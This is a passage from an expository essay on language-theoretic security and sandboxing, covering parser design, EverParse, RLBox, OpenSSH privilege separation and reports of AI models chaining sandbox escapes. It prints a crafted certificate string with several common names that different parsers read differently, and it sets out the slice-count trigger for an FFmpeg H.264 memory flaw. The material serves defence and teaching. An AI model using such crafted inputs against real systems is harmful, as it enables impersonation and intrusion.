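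Parsing a *context-sensitive* language can require memory proportional to the input's length. *Seventy Years of Parsing* (Lucas, Anantharaman and Smith, 2026) gives the example of a number followed by that many letters, where "3aaa" is valid and "2aaa" isn't. Such length fields are common in binary formats, including PNG images and internet packets.

At the top of the hierarchy, the input can be a program in a *Turing-complete* language, which can express any computation. If "valid" means that the program eventually finishes, no recogniser can always give the right answer, because deciding whether a program finishes is the halting problem.

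| Class | Memory needed | Worst-case time for n bytes | Can an algorithm always tell whether two grammars accept the same inputs? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Regular | Fixed | Proportional to n | Yes |
| Deterministic context-free | A stack | Proportional to n | Yes |
| Context-free in general | A stack, plus guessing | n³ | No |
| Context-sensitive | Proportional to n | 2ⁿ | No |
| Turing-complete | Unlimited | May never finish | No |

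The times are for general methods that work on every language in the class. Particular languages can be much easier. For example, a recogniser can check a simple length field in one pass.

### Use the weakest language that does the job

Sassaman and colleagues' first principle is that an input language should be no more powerful than its purpose requires. One reason is that validity can be undecidable for a Turing-complete language, much as Rice's theorem rules out a perfect checker for programs. Any check the developers write will then differ somewhere from the check they believe they wrote, and more testing won't fix that.

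Programs query databases in SQL, and developers often try to stop attackers from slipping commands into these queries by searching the input for forbidden patterns. They use regular expressions, which can describe only regular languages. Sassaman and colleagues point out that SQL was context-free even in its earlier form and that recursive queries later made it Turing-complete, so pattern searches could not cover it. In 2005, Robert Hansen and Patterson proposed a better method, which is to identify the few kinds of query an application needs, define them as a small language and generate a parser for it.

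The other reason is that an attacker can use whatever computing power the input-handling code has. For example, a video decoder might have several small bugs. One kind of malformed frame makes it copy a number from one place in memory to another, a second makes it add two numbers, and a third makes it skip ahead if a number is zero. No single frame does much harm. But ordinary programs consist of instructions like these, so a long file of such frames is a program that the decoder runs.

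LangSec researchers call this a *weird machine*, an unintended computer made out of a program's bugs and ordinary features, with the crafted input as its software. A recogniser for a regular language gives an attacker much less to work with, because it has no memory beyond its current state. The code behind the recogniser is unchanged, though, and may still have bugs that a valid input can reach.

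### One certificate, three readings

The second principle covers programs that have to read the same message in the same way. A website proves its identity to a browser with a certificate, a file in which a certificate authority vouches that the holder controls a name such as www.bank.com. In 2009 Dan Kaminsky, Patterson and Sassaman tested how different programs read unusual certificates. Programmers had written most of the parsers by hand, because the specification wasn't in a form that a parser generator could easily use. One certificate contained this series of "common names":

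```
CN=www.badguy.com/CN=www.bank.com/CN=www.bank2.com/CN=*
```

OpenSSL, a widely used security library, returned only the first name. Internet Explorer accepted the certificate for both banks. Firefox treated the asterisk as a wildcard and accepted it for every site.

Suppose an attacker owns badguy.com and applies to an authority whose software relies on OpenSSL. The software reads one name, the attacker proves control of it, and the authority signs the certificate. The attacker can now pose as either bank to anyone using Internet Explorer, and as any site to anyone using Firefox. No program has crashed or corrupted memory. Someone who reviewed OpenSSL alone could easily miss the problem, because it arises only when another program reads the certificate differently.

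Sassaman and colleagues therefore recommend that communicating programs use only regular or deterministic context-free languages. An algorithm can determine whether two grammars for these languages accept exactly the same inputs. No general algorithm exists for the more powerful classes in the table, so testers can only try examples, which can't guarantee that two grammars match.

Programs that accept the same inputs can still interpret them differently. All three programs accepted the certificate but did not all identify the same owner. Lucas and colleagues discuss a stricter condition, *structural equivalence*, which also requires two grammars to break up every input in the same way. Even this might not have helped here, since OpenSSL could have separated all four names correctly and still returned the first. A surer remedy is to allow only one name per certificate, which leaves much less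 room for different interpretations.

*Certified Splitting* (2026) applies the theory of regular languages to tokenisers, the components that cut text into words and symbols. Given two sets of regular rules, its method decides whether any text exists that they would cut in different places, and produces an example if so. If none exists, the two sets cut every possible input in the same places, which no finite set of tests could establish.

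Most programs that exchange messages have no such guarantee. Andarzian, Meyers and Poll (2025), in *Email Smuggling with Differential Fuzzing of MIME Parsers*, examine MIME, the standard that lets emails carry attachments. A mail server, a spam or virus filter and the recipient's mail program may all parse the same email, each with its own code. In the attack they study, a single email appears to the recipient as two. Chen (2026), in *Defensive Handling of MIME Parsing Ambiguities in Email Delivery*, a draft internet standard, adds that gateways and mail programs differ in how they recover from errors. If a filter and a mail program divide a malformed message differently, the filter may never scan the attachment that the user opens.

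The same problem affects scanners for AI models. Developers often save models in pickle, a Python format whose files contain instructions that Python runs when it loads them. In a paper at the 2026 LangSec workshop, Justin Applegate and Andreas Kellas compared Python's three built-in modules for reading pickle files and found 14 new discrepancies. Attackers could use four of them to get past security scanners like those on Hugging Face, a popular site for sharing models. In such cases the scanner, which acts as the security reviewer, interprets the file differently from the module that loads it.

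### The frame with 65,536 slices

LangSec researchers use the term *shotgun parser* for input checks that are spread through a program and mixed with its ordinary work. Such checks are a problem because programmers tend to write each part of the program as if some other part had already checked the data. The 16-year-old flaw in FFmpeg's H.264 decoder is an example.

H.264 divides each frame into slices, and each slice is a run of blocks of 16 by 16 pixels, called macroblocks. When the decoder smooths the edges between blocks, it sometimes has to know whether a neighbouring block belongs to the same slice. It looks this up in a table that has an entry for every position in the frame, with some padding around the edge. As Carlini and colleagues explain, the attack works like this:

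1. Each entry has 16 bits, so it can hold a number from 0 to 65,535. The counter that numbers the slices has 32 bits and no upper limit.
2. FFmpeg starts by filling the table with 65,535, which it uses as a marker for "no slice here".
3. An attacker makes a frame with 65,536 slices. The numbering starts at 0, so the last one is slice 65,535.
4. A block in that slice, at the edge of the frame, looks up its neighbour and finds 65,535 in the padding. The numbers match, so the decoder concludes that the neighbour exists.
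5. The decoder writes outside the memory it is entitled to use, and crashes.

Carlini and colleagues think it would be hard to turn this into a takeover, since the attacker can write only a few bytes. The marker dates from 2003 and became exploitable when the code was reorganised in 2010. Real videos have only a few slices per frame, so nobody ran into the problem by accident.

A declared limit of 65,535 slices per frame would have rejected the file. But a format designer would be unlikely to think of that number, because it follows from the size of a table entry and the choice of a marker in one particular decoder. A designer who wanted slice numbers to fit in 16 bits would have allowed 65,536 slices, which is one too many for that decoder.

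Capping every quantity at a little more than real files use would have been enough. A cap of 256 slices would have blocked the file without anyone needing to know about the marker. Checking that a specification gives every number an upper limit is a narrow task that a program can do. Judging whether each limit is tight enough is harder, although developers can compare the limits with the files that customers upload.

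A limit on frame size could also have blocked the flaw, even if it was set only to save memory. If each macroblock belongs to only one slice, 65,536 slices need at least 65,536 macroblocks, and therefore a frame of at least 4,096 by 4,096 pixels or the equivalent area. If the thumbnail service had refused anything larger than 3,840 by 2,160 pixels, no accepted frame could have had more than 32,400 macroblocks. As long as the recogniser also refused overlapping slices, attackers could not have reached the flaw.

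InfoQ (2026) describes PixelSmash, another FFmpeg flaw involving slices, which is in the decoder for the MagicYUV format. The seven-line patch begins by testing for a slice height of zero or less. Any designer could have written down the rule that a slice must have a positive height, unlike the limit on H.264 slices. Every Linux package that the researchers tested had the decoder switched on, although few services need it. Administrators who couldn't upgrade could rebuild FFmpeg without MagicYUV, and anyone running a service that never needed the format could have done so years earlier.

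A recogniser that checks input on arrival doesn't help if the program later alters the data and assumes it is still valid. Checking the data again in every function would be slow. At the 2026 LangSec workshop, J. Peter Brady and Sean Smith presented a tool that traces which functions change a piece of data and which merely pass it along, so that developers can add checks only where the data has changed.

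### Parsers that come with a proof

Handwritten recognisers have bugs like any other code. An alternative is to describe the format in a specification and let a tool write the recogniser. EverParse, from Microsoft Research, does this and also proves that the result matches the specification. Developers write the specification in a language called 3D, which resembles the way C programmers already describe data. Here is one for a frame in an invented video format:

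```
typedef struct _FRAME {
  UINT32 Width      { 16 <= Width  && Width  <= 3840 };
  UINT32 Height     { 16 <= Height && Height <= 2160 };
  UINT32 SliceCount { 1 <= SliceCount && SliceCount <= 256 };
  UINT32 DataLength { DataLength <= 4000000 };
  UINT8  Data[:byte-size DataLength];
} FRAME;
```

From such a description, EverParse generates a C function that checks a block of bytes. *Access Control as Verified Parse Constraints* (2026) states the main guarantee as a theorem. For every block of bytes b and every length ℓ,

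accept(b, ℓ) = true ⇔ |b| ≥ ℓ and the fields in the first ℓ bytes of b satisfy the specification

The proof must show that the function accepts every valid input and rejects every invalid one. It would therefore fail for a parser that rejected everything.

*Hardening Attack Surfaces with Formally Proven Binary Format Parsers* (Swamy, Ramananandro and colleagues, 2022) also describes guarantees that the code EverParse generates is memory-safe, even though it is in C, and that its arithmetic can't overflow. EverParse checks the specification for overflow too. It would reject a rule that multiplied width by height without first limiting both, which rules out the mistake behind the thumbnail service's picture of 65,536 by 65,536 pixels.

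The code also never reads the same byte twice. This matters when a virtual machine shares memory with the computer that hosts it, because a malicious virtual machine could change a packet after the host has checked it but before the host uses it. If the host reads each byte only once and copies what it needs as it goes, the data it uses is the same data it checked.

EverParse's 3D language can describe length fields, which are context-sensitive in general. It has no recursion, so it can't directly describe brackets nested to any depth, even though these are lower in the Chomsky hierarchy. This is a sensible trade because binary formats need length fields more often than deep nesting. There is no general test for whether two parsers are equivalent, but two parsers that EverParse generates from the same specification accept the same inputs because both match it exactly.

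Microsoft has used EverParse since 2019 in Hyper-V, the software that runs virtual machines on Windows and in its Azure cloud. The parsers it generates check messages passing through a virtual network switch, which runs in the core of the host's operating system and receives untrusted data from the virtual machines. Swamy and colleagues report that EverParse generated and verified more than 23,000 lines of C in 82 seconds from about 5,000 lines of specification for the switch. By 2025, verified code was checking every network packet that passed through Hyper-V, according to *EverParse*, Ramananandro's slides for an internet standards meeting.

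Microsoft would accept the new parsers only if they used at most 2 percent more processor time per byte than the old ones. The new parsers met this limit and were slightly faster in some configurations because they made fewer copies.

The security evidence is encouraging but incomplete. A separate team reviewed and fuzzed the parsers and found no bugs in the parsing code, but Microsoft hasn't published the details, and Swamy and colleagues don't count how many vulnerabilities the change removed. After the change, several fuzzers stopped working effectively because the parsers rejected every input the fuzzers generated. Microsoft's engineers then began using the specifications to produce well-formed inputs that would reach the code behind the parsers, and a competent attacker can do the same. Swamy and colleagues say that verified parsing doesn't guarantee the security of the whole switch.

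### Who checks the specification?

Reviewers can read 5,000 lines of specification instead of a much larger amount of parsing code. The proof checks that the code matches the specification, but a person still has to decide whether the specification describes the right format. Writing the specification for Hyper-V took about one person-year, according to Ramananandro in *From Legacy to Verified Parsers with AI*. Some of the formats were proprietary and had changed over many years, so the engineers had to piece together the rules from documents, code and tests.

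AI can do much of this writing. *3DGen* (2024) describes AI agents that draft a 3D specification from the documentation or from existing code. A separate tool generates test packets, the system compares the results with those of an older parser where one exists, and the agents revise the draft. Its developers tried it on 20 network protocols with a version of GPT-4, and current models are far more capable. But a better model can't recover a rule that neither the documents nor the code contains. Ramananandro concludes that people must still review the specifications, and adds that with AI drafting, people who only approve a specification lose some of the understanding of its rules that they would gain by writing it by hand.

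The FFmpeg flaw shows why agreement with an older program is a poor test of a specification. An agent that learned the H.264 format from FFmpeg's code would have found no limit on slices and might well have left the limit out of its specification. The specification would then have matched FFmpeg despite the omission. Julien Vanegue of Bloomberg warned of this circularity in a 2026 LangSec workshop talk about using language models to infer specifications from millions of lines of open-source code.

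### Formats that nobody can simplify

An input format is easiest to restrict when one organisation controls both the sender and the receiver. One of Hyper-V's formats originally allowed padding between two fields. The engineers decided that the padding was wasteful, so their specification requires the second field to start at exactly byte 12. They could impose this rule because Microsoft also wrote the software that sends the messages.

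PDF is the opposite case, because billions of files already exist and many different programs produce them. In a comparison of eleven common formats by Lucas and colleagues, only PDF needs the full power of a Turing machine. A PDF contains a table of positions that makes the parser jump back and forth through the file, and it can embed fonts, images and JavaScript. A recogniser can check that the JavaScript is syntactically correct, but if validity also requires the scripts to run without error, it is undecidable.

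DARPA, the research agency of the US Department of Defense, set up a programme called SafeDocs to apply LangSec to formats like this. It justified the programme by saying that 80 percent of the problems in the main public catalogue of vulnerabilities involve failures of input validation, a figure Kathleen Fisher of Tufts University cited in a keynote at the LangSec (2021) workshop. The figure doesn't show how many of those vulnerabilities a recogniser would have stopped. The FFmpeg flaw would presumably count as a failure of input validation, but even a perfect recogniser for H.264 would have let the file through if nobody had declared the limit.

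SafeDocs researchers kept PDF and worked on exact, machine-readable descriptions of the format and on tools that turn such descriptions into parsers. One tool, DaeDaLus, generates C++ parsers that can follow jumps between positions in a file, which simpler tools can't handle. The PDF Association produced the Arlington PDF Model, which lists the objects a PDF may contain and the values they may have. With a description like this, an organisation can define a smaller PDF format for its own use, for example one without JavaScript, and reject files that don't conform. This works for a court that can tell lawyers how to file documents, but not for a general-purpose PDF reader, which has to open whatever its users receive.

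It would be easier to leave scripting out of a format at the start than to remove it later, because removing a feature people rely on breaks their documents. Sassaman and colleagues complained in 2011 that HTML5 was Turing-complete, unlike HTML4. In a talk at the 2024 LangSec workshop, Will Crichton and Shriram Krishnamurthi asked whether a new document language could be secure by construction, but files in the old formats would still exist.

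Even where a format has clear rules, developers feel pressure to tolerate files that break them. The early internet engineer Jon Postel advised programmers to be conservative in what they send and liberal in what they accept, which helped different systems work together when the internet was young. But two liberal programs will often repair the same malformed message in different ways, and an attacker can use the difference to smuggle an email past a filter. If one popular program produces malformed messages, others also have to accept them, and strict checking soon becomes impractical for everyone.

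Ramananandro suggests keeping the first half of Postel's advice and being "paranoid" about what one receives. This is good advice for a new protocol, but it has a drawback for the thumbnail service. If 2 percent of customers' phones produce slightly faulty videos that play fine everywhere else, a strict recogniser will reject those videos, and the customers will soon complain to the developers.

### Well formed but harmful

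A recogniser checks whether an input has the right form, so it will accept a customer's well-formed request for a thumbnail of another customer's video. Designers can put some access rules into the format. *Access Control as Verified Parse Constraints* does this for rules about which roles may perform which actions, so a request that breaks the policy also fails to parse. But the parser can only compare the bytes it receives, so another part of the service has to detect a request that names the wrong customer.

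The same limit applies to messages between AI agents. Max von Hippel and Evan Miyazono argued at the 2025 LangSec workshop that AI security is a LangSec problem, because models produce structured output and call tools that have to parse it. Hugo O'Connor's *CBCL* (2026) is a language for such messages that stays deterministic context-free even when agents add vocabulary. A proof checker has confirmed that these additions can't expand without limit or redefine the core vocabulary. This protects the program that parses a message, but not necessarily the agent that acts on it, because a message may include ordinary English, and no grammar separates harmful English sentences from harmless ones.

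The thumbnail service can still reject a lot of bad input before decoding, including oversized pictures, data that doesn't match its declared length, links to other files and names with slashes in them. The compressed video is harder to check because H.264 packs its data so tightly that a recogniser often can't find where one value ends and the next begins without doing much of the decoder's work. A complete recogniser would therefore be a large program that could easily have bugs of its own. Unless somebody builds one and proves it correct, the developers have to expect that a bad file will sometimes reach the decoder.

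## Sandboxing: limiting what a compromised program can do

A *sandbox* limits what a program can reach, even after an attacker has taken it over. If the thumbnail service's decoder runs in a sandbox, a reviewer can assume that some video will take it over and ask what the attacker could reach from there. This is usually much easier than working out whether any possible video could take over the decoder, which the reviewer would have to do without a sandbox, because what the attacker can reach depends on a list of permissions and not on the details of the video code.

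### Processes and system calls

Operating systems already run each program in a *process* with its own memory, which other processes normally can't touch. To affect anything outside, such as a file or a network connection, a process has to make a *system call*, a request to the *kernel*, the core of the operating system. Linux has several hundred system calls, and an ordinary program can use most of them with all the rights of its user's account. A process sandbox removes most of this access. On Linux, for example, a program can install a seccomp-bpf filter, and the kernel then refuses any call the filter doesn't allow.

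Bernstein (2007), in *Some thoughts on security after ten years of qmail 1.0*, describes an "extreme sandbox" for a program that converts JPEG pictures into plain bitmaps. It uses only features that Unix systems already had. Before the converter runs, a launcher does the following:

- It sets the number of new files and network connections the converter may open to zero.
- It makes an empty folder the only part of the disk the converter can see.
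- It gives the converter a user number that no other process has, so that it can't interfere with anything else that is running.
- It forbids the converter to start other processes.
- It limits how much memory the converter can take.

The converter can still read the picture and write the bitmap, because the launcher opened both channels in advance. An attacker who takes over the converter can produce any bitmap, but they could have done that by sending a different picture. Setting these limits requires no knowledge of JPEG, and a reviewer can check them without reading the converter's code.

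However, the kernel has to enforce all of these restrictions correctly. The sandbox removes the converter from the trusted computing base but leaves the kernel in it. The Linux kernel has tens of millions of lines of code, although many are in drivers for hardware that any one machine lacks.

### Keeping every memory access in bounds

Switching between processes takes time, which matters when a program calls a library often. Firefox's JPEG library returns a picture one row at a time, so a large picture takes thousands of calls. *Software fault isolation* avoids the switching by keeping the library in the same process as the program that uses it. A special compiler adds instructions to the library that confine it to its own part of memory.

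Suppose the library's part of memory runs from address 5,000,000 to address 5,999,999. Before every read or write, the compiler inserts code that keeps the last six digits of the address and sets the first digit to 5. Address 5,123,456 stays the same. If an attacker has corrupted a pointer to hold 8,123,456, the code changes it to 5,123,456 too, so the write can damage only the library's own data. Real systems do this with binary digits, which takes an instruction or two.

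The compiler also restricts where the library's code can jump, so that the library can't skip the inserted instructions. Google's Native Client, a system of this kind, has a separate verifier that examines the finished machine code and rejects it if any access lacks protection, so nobody has to trust the compiler. Narayan, Disselkoen and colleagues (2020) heavily altered Native Client's compiler for their experiments in *Retrofitting Fine Grain Isolation in the Firefox Renderer*, but ran everything it produced through the original verifier.

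WebAssembly, a portable code format that all major browsers can run, achieves much the same result by a different method. A pointer in WebAssembly is a 32-bit distance from the start of the program's own block of memory, so the program cannot express an address before that block. Many systems that run WebAssembly reserve the whole range of addresses a pointer can reach and make the unused part inaccessible. Firefox uses WebAssembly to confine libraries written in C and C++. Mozilla's *WebAssembly and Back Again* (2021) explains that its engineers compile a library to WebAssembly and then translate the result back into C, which their usual tools can build into the browser.

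An attacker can still use the library's memory faults to take over the library, but not to reach the rest of the program directly.

### What the walls cost

Narayan and colleagues put six of Firefox's decoding and decompression libraries into both kinds of sandbox and loaded eleven websites. An ordinary call to an empty function took 0.02 microseconds on their machine.

| | Software fault isolation | Separate process |
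|---|---|---|
| Creating a sandbox | about 1 ms | about 2 ms |
| Calling an empty function | 0.22 µs | 0.47 µs, or 7.4 µs if the process sleeps between calls |
| Extra page-loading time | 3% | 13% |
| Extra memory at the peak | 25% | 18% |

A picture with 2,000 rows needs at least 2,000 calls. Those calls would take about 0.4 milliseconds with software fault isolation and 15 milliseconds with a process that sleeps between calls. To reduce the page-loading overhead from 167 percent to the 13 percent in the table, Narayan and colleagues had to reserve a processor core for the sandboxes and let them wait in a busy loop during urgent work. The extra memory use is temporary, since the browser can discard a sandbox once it has decoded the picture.

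Sandboxing slowed video the least. 4K test videos played at the normal frame rate in both kinds of sandbox, which is encouraging for a thumbnail service. When Mozilla first used WebAssembly in a released browser, it was slower than Native Client. It made Graphite, a library for complex fonts, 85 percent slower, but people rarely load such fonts and wouldn't notice the delay.

A *virtual machine* imitates a whole computer, including its own kernel. An attacker who takes over that kernel must still get through the virtual machine monitor, which can be much smaller than a general-purpose kernel. Carlini and colleagues note that nearly everything in the public cloud runs in virtual machines, and that cloud companies assume their customers may attack one another. Each virtual machine needs its own operating system, which takes up memory and time to start. This overhead is acceptable for separating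 two companies that rent the same computer, but excessive for separating two pictures on a web page. All three kinds of sandbox depend on the processor working as its makers describe.

### OpenSSH: a privileged monitor with few duties

OpenSSH lets people log in to a computer over the internet. Its server needs root privilege for a few jobs, such as opening a terminal for each new user. In early versions, the process that handled connections from strangers held this privilege the whole time, so one memory fault in it could let an attacker take control of the entire machine.

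In *Preventing Privilege Escalation*, Provos, Friedl and Honeyman (2003) split the server into two processes. An unprivileged process handles the network traffic under its own account, with file access limited to an empty folder. The other process, the monitor, keeps root privilege and performs the few operations that need it when the unprivileged process requests them.

The monitor accepts only requests that fit the current stage of a login. At the start, the unprivileged process can request the numbers it needs to set up encryption and a signature that proves the server's identity. Next it can have the monitor check a user name, and only then a password. If it makes a request out of turn, the monitor shuts down. Only the monitor holds the server's private key, and it signs for the unprivileged process, so an attacker who controls that process might obtain a signature but can't steal the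 key. After a successful login, a new process continues with the user's rights. If it needs a terminal, the monitor opens one and passes it a reference.

Including libraries, 8,391 of the server's 25,980 lines of code (32.3 percent) stayed privileged. For OpenSSH's own code the share was about 25 percent, and the monitor accounted for 900 lines. The engineers had to change only 2 percent of the existing source, but they added about 3,000 lines. Logins and file transfers took less than 1 percent longer.

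Provos and colleagues infer that about two thirds of future errors won't give an attacker extra privilege. This is a rough estimate, because it assumes that errors are spread evenly through the code. Past flaws are better evidence, and the paper goes through five that the split would have contained:

- Three let a stranger become root: an integer overflow in the code that processes network packets, a memory error in the zlib compression library, and a fault in one method of logging in.
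- Two let a logged-in user become root: an off-by-one error in the code for communication channels, and a bug in the handling of Kerberos tickets, a kind of network credential.

With the split, the attacker who hadn't logged in would have gained control of a process with access to no files outside an empty folder, and the logged-in user would have gained nothing new. Five cases are a small sample, but some of these flaws were unknown when the engineers built the split, so it can't have been designed around those. The zlib error was in another project's code, so no review of OpenSSH's own source could have found it.

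An attacker who controls the unprivileged process can still open network connections from the server and waste its resources. Provos and colleagues also assume that the kernel's system calls are secure. Even so, the benefit was large for such a small change, and OpenSSH has since made privilege separation mandatory.

### RLBox: checking what comes back

Browsers run the *renderer*, the part that processes web pages, in a sandboxed process. The sandbox protects the computer's files, but Narayan and colleagues point out that nearly everything people care about now happens on websites. An attacker who takes over the renderer with a malicious audio file might gain control of the victim's email without leaving the sandbox. In 2018, contestants at a hacking competition broke into Firefox through a flaw in an audio library.

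Narayan and colleagues' RLBox framework puts a second sandbox inside the renderer, around a single library. Media libraries suit this well because they need little access. An attacker who takes over an image decoder can at worst change how some images look. Sandboxing the JavaScript engine would achieve little, since whoever controls it already controls the web page.

Keeping the library out of the renderer's memory isn't enough, because programmers wrote the renderer assuming that its libraries would return correct data. For example, the JPEG library keeps count of the row it has reached, and the renderer uses that number to work out where in its own memory to put the pixels. If an attacker takes over the library and makes it report row 1,000,000 of a picture with 600 rows, the renderer will write pixels far outside the picture's memory, even though the library has stayed inside its sandbox.

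RLBox prevents this by marking everything that comes out of the sandbox as *tainted*. A whole number becomes a `tainted<int>`, which the compiler won't let the renderer use as an ordinary number until a short function called a *validator* has checked it. In simplified form:

```cpp
tainted<int> reported = sandbox_invoke(decoder, current_row);
int row = reported.verify([&](int r) {
    return (r >= 0 && r < height) ? r : 0;
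});
```

Here `height` is a number the renderer has already checked. Anything the renderer calculates from a tainted value is also tainted. If a tainted value is in memory that the renderer shares with the library, RLBox copies it before checking it, because the library could otherwise change it between the check and the use. EverParse guards against the same kind of change by reading each byte only once.

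Across the six libraries, RLBox identified 100 places where the renderer needed to check data from a sandbox. The programmers covered these with 35 validators, averaging two to four lines each. RLBox added 138 pointer checks automatically. Moving a library into a sandbox took a little over two days on average, and the library's own code didn't have to change.

The compiler does the narrow task of confirming that every tainted value goes through a validator. Someone still has to decide whether each validator is right, which requires knowing what the value means and what the renderer will do with it. Narayan and colleagues found this the hardest part of the work, and their security claims assume that the validators are correct. A programmer can also skip the check by calling `unsafeUnverified`, which a text search can find as easily as Rust's `unsafe`.

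Firefox first used RLBox in 2020, to sandbox Graphite. By December 2021, Firefox used it for five modules: Graphite, a spelling checker, and the code that handles an audio and video container, a text format and compressed web fonts (The Hacker News, 2021). Changelog's *Fine-grained sandboxing in Firefox 95* quotes Mozilla as saying that even an unknown flaw in any of them should pose no threat to Firefox, "assuming we did it right".

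### The Rule of 2

Safe languages, simple formats and sandboxes can partly substitute for one another. Chromium's Rule of 2 makes this a policy. A developer whose code combines untrustworthy input, an unsafe language and high privilege can comply by removing any one of the three. Willison (2025), in *Chromium Docs*, dates the rule to 2019.

Developers can remove the unsafe language by writing the code in something like Rust or Java, or remove the privilege by running it in a sandboxed process. Chromium counts any process with the rights of a user's account as highly privileged, so running without root isn't enough.

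Input is harder to make trustworthy. A program can accept it only from a known company, with cryptographic proof of where it came from, or convert it into something simpler. For example, a sandboxed process can decode a PNG picture into a plain grid of pixels and pass the grid to a more privileged process. A malicious PNG may take over the first process, but the second reads only a width, a height and a run of colour values, so its parser can be short enough to get right.

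The rule has drawbacks, and Chromium doesn't always follow it. On Windows, the process that handles network traffic is written in C++, reads data from anyone on the internet and has no sandbox by default. It also handles traffic for many websites at once. Chromium's developers want to give each site its own network process, but processes use memory, and on Android the system then shuts down other apps and browser tabs far more often. They have also had to hold back features because another process would have used too many resources. They concluded that they were reaching the limits of sandboxing, and that removing memory faults from the code had become a more practical way to stay ahead of attackers.

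### Bernstein's objection

Bernstein wrote qmail, a mail server that ran on more than a million machines by 2007. In 1997 he offered $500 to the first person to find a security hole in it, and ten years later nobody had claimed the money. He had divided qmail among several accounts with limited rights and once recommended this as a security measure. In his retrospective, he says the division didn't help at all and that qmail was secure because it had very few bugs.

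Bernstein objects that lowering a program's privilege is not the same as reducing the amount of trusted code. Code is untrusted only if nothing it does can violate the user's security requirements. One of his examples is a helper program that looked up internet addresses for the Netscape browser. Researchers had confined it so that it couldn't read the disk, but an attacker who took it over could still give Netscape false addresses and steal the user's web connections. The helper's bugs were still dangerous after the confinement, so somebody still had to find and fix them. Bernstein concludes that minimising privilege doesn't bring a secure system any closer.

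He makes a related complaint about virtual machines and "secure" operating systems. They can isolate a mail program from other programs, but they don't stop one malicious message from corrupting the mail program's other messages.

In *Towards a Theory of Application Compartmentalisation*, Watson, Murdoch and colleagues in effect reply to Bernstein, though they don't mention him. They model a program as a set of inputs and outputs, and give each input-output pair a probability that malicious input leads to malicious output. For example, a malicious video might have a 50 percent chance of corrupting its thumbnail and, because the decoder has full access, a 50 percent chance of corrupting the company's password file. A sandbox might leave the first figure at 50 percent and cut the second to 1 percent. The decoder is as easy to take over as before, but the attacker is much less likely to reach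 the password file. Bernstein counts only whether a bug can do *some* harm, so his measure misses this improvement.

But he is right that the remaining harm depends on whose data the program handles. His own JPEG sandbox limits that harm by giving the converter one picture from one source, so an attacker who controls it can spoil only their own picture. By Bernstein's definition, the converter is no longer trusted code. The Netscape helper, by contrast, handled addresses for every site the user visited, so confining it to fewer files was bound to leave a serious danger.

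The successful designs mostly follow this pattern. OpenSSH starts a new unprivileged process for each connection, so an attacker who takes one over controls only their own login attempt. RLBox can use a separate sandbox for each combination of library, website and content type. A malicious image may then affect other images from the same site, but not the site's scripts or anything from another site.

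The thumbnail service should likewise start a new sandbox for every video, which adds only about two milliseconds each time. This also fixes the reused-frame fault that Rust didn't fix, because a fresh process has never held another customer's frames. If the decoder can't open documents, a file that points to a private document can't expose it. Limits on memory and time stop files from exhausting the machine. A malicious update to the decoding library could still produce wrong thumbnails, but it couldn't send the videos to a stranger over the network.

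### Confining old software

Much of the world's software was written on the assumption that a program should have all the rights of the person running it. Trillions of dollars have gone into that software, and nobody is likely to replace it all, even if the danger would justify the expense. Confinement offers a way to keep using it more safely. Engineers can build a secure system and, inside it, faithfully imitate the insecure environment an old program was written for. The program finds files and a network in the usual places, but it can reach only those the engineers chose to provide. The verified kernel seL4, for instance, can run a copy of Linux this way. Safer programs can then replace the old ones gradually, while everything keeps working.

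RLBox supports this argument, since two days of work per library is much less than a rewrite. But the argument is weaker than it was before 2026, because Bun's port to Rust took only 11 days. Sandboxing and rewriting can also be combined, as Bun still depends on large C and C++ libraries that its developers didn't port.

Confining an old program protects everything else from it, but does little to protect the data the program itself can access. If a hospital runs an old records system in a virtual machine, an intruder who breaks into that system may be unable to reach the heating controls or the payroll, but can still read and alter the patients' records.

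### How sandboxes fail

A confined program has to communicate with a process outside, which usually has more privilege. The more kinds of request that process accepts, the larger the attack surface. OpenSSH's monitor accepts very few, but a browser's main process has to accept many. In May 2026, Mozilla's *Behind the Scenes Hardening Firefox with Claude Mythos Preview* listed flaws that its engineers had found with AI models. One flaw let a compromised web-page process send any picture as wallpaper to Firefox's privileged parent process, which would decode it. The parent was therefore doing risky work that the sandbox was meant to contain, although an attacker would also have needed a flaw in an image decoder. Sending a plain grid of pixels, as the Rule of 2 suggests, would have avoided the problem. Mozilla observes that finding this flaw required reasoning about how far the parent could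 trust its inputs, which is difficult to automate.

Processes on the same machine also share a kernel, so a flaw in a system call that the filter allows may let an attacker get past every process sandbox on the machine. Carlini and colleagues report nearly a dozen cases in which Mythos Preview combined two, three or four flaws to go from an ordinary Linux account to full control. A strict filter blocks some of these routes by making the faulty part of the kernel unreachable. A virtual machine adds another barrier, but its monitor can have flaws too, like the one found in a memory-safe monitor.

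Faults in the sandbox's own code are the hardest to plan for. Mozilla's list includes one in RLBox, which PPC Land describes as a gap in the logic that checks values leaving the sandbox. Every sandboxed library relies on this code, so a mistake in it matters more than a mistake in a single validator. PPC Land adds that the sandbox escapes on the list weren't complete attacks, because each required an attacker to have already taken over a process.

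A program confined to its own memory may still obtain information about its neighbours by timing its own work, even if the sandbox has no fault. Narayan and colleagues leave out these side channels, including attacks such as Spectre, which exploit the way processors guess which instructions come next and run them early.

### Friction and hard barriers

In early 2026, Anthropic reported that one of its Claude models had written browser exploits that worked only in a test version without the sandbox. In April, Carlini and colleagues reported that Mythos Preview had written a browser exploit that chained four flaws and escaped both the renderer's sandbox and the operating system's. With help from the researchers, it also produced a web page that could let an attacker write to the kernel of any visitor's computer.

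Carlini and colleagues distinguish defences that mainly add friction, making an attack tedious but not impossible, from those that impose hard barriers. They expect hard barriers to remain important, but defences that rely on friction may become much weaker because a model can work through tedious steps quickly.

A chain of sandboxes can do little more than slow an attacker down. An attacker with a copy of the browser can work on each layer separately and keep any flaws they find. If finding a usable flaw takes 200 attempts per layer on average, four layers take about 800 attempts, not 200 to the fourth power. Combining the flaws takes more work, but for an attacker with a capable model, a fourfold increase in attempts may just mean spending more money. A layer with no usable flaw stops the attack however many attempts the attacker makes.

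Carlini and colleagues give two examples of a hard barrier. One is loading the kernel at a random place in memory so that attackers don't know where to write. Whether this is a hard barrier is debatable, because the location can leak. Their article describes Mythos Preview getting past it by first finding a flaw that revealed the location, and also mentions a place where the Linux kernel deliberately discloses one of its addresses. The other example, a rule that no memory may be both writable and executable, holds even against an attacker who knows everything about the system, though it blocks only one step of an attack.

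Layered defences can be worth having even when no layer is perfect. Mythos Preview found many remotely triggerable flaws in the Linux kernel, but after several thousand scans it hadn't exploited any of them. Carlini and colleagues attribute this to the kernel's layered defences. This result is for one model in the spring of 2026, and a stronger model may do better.

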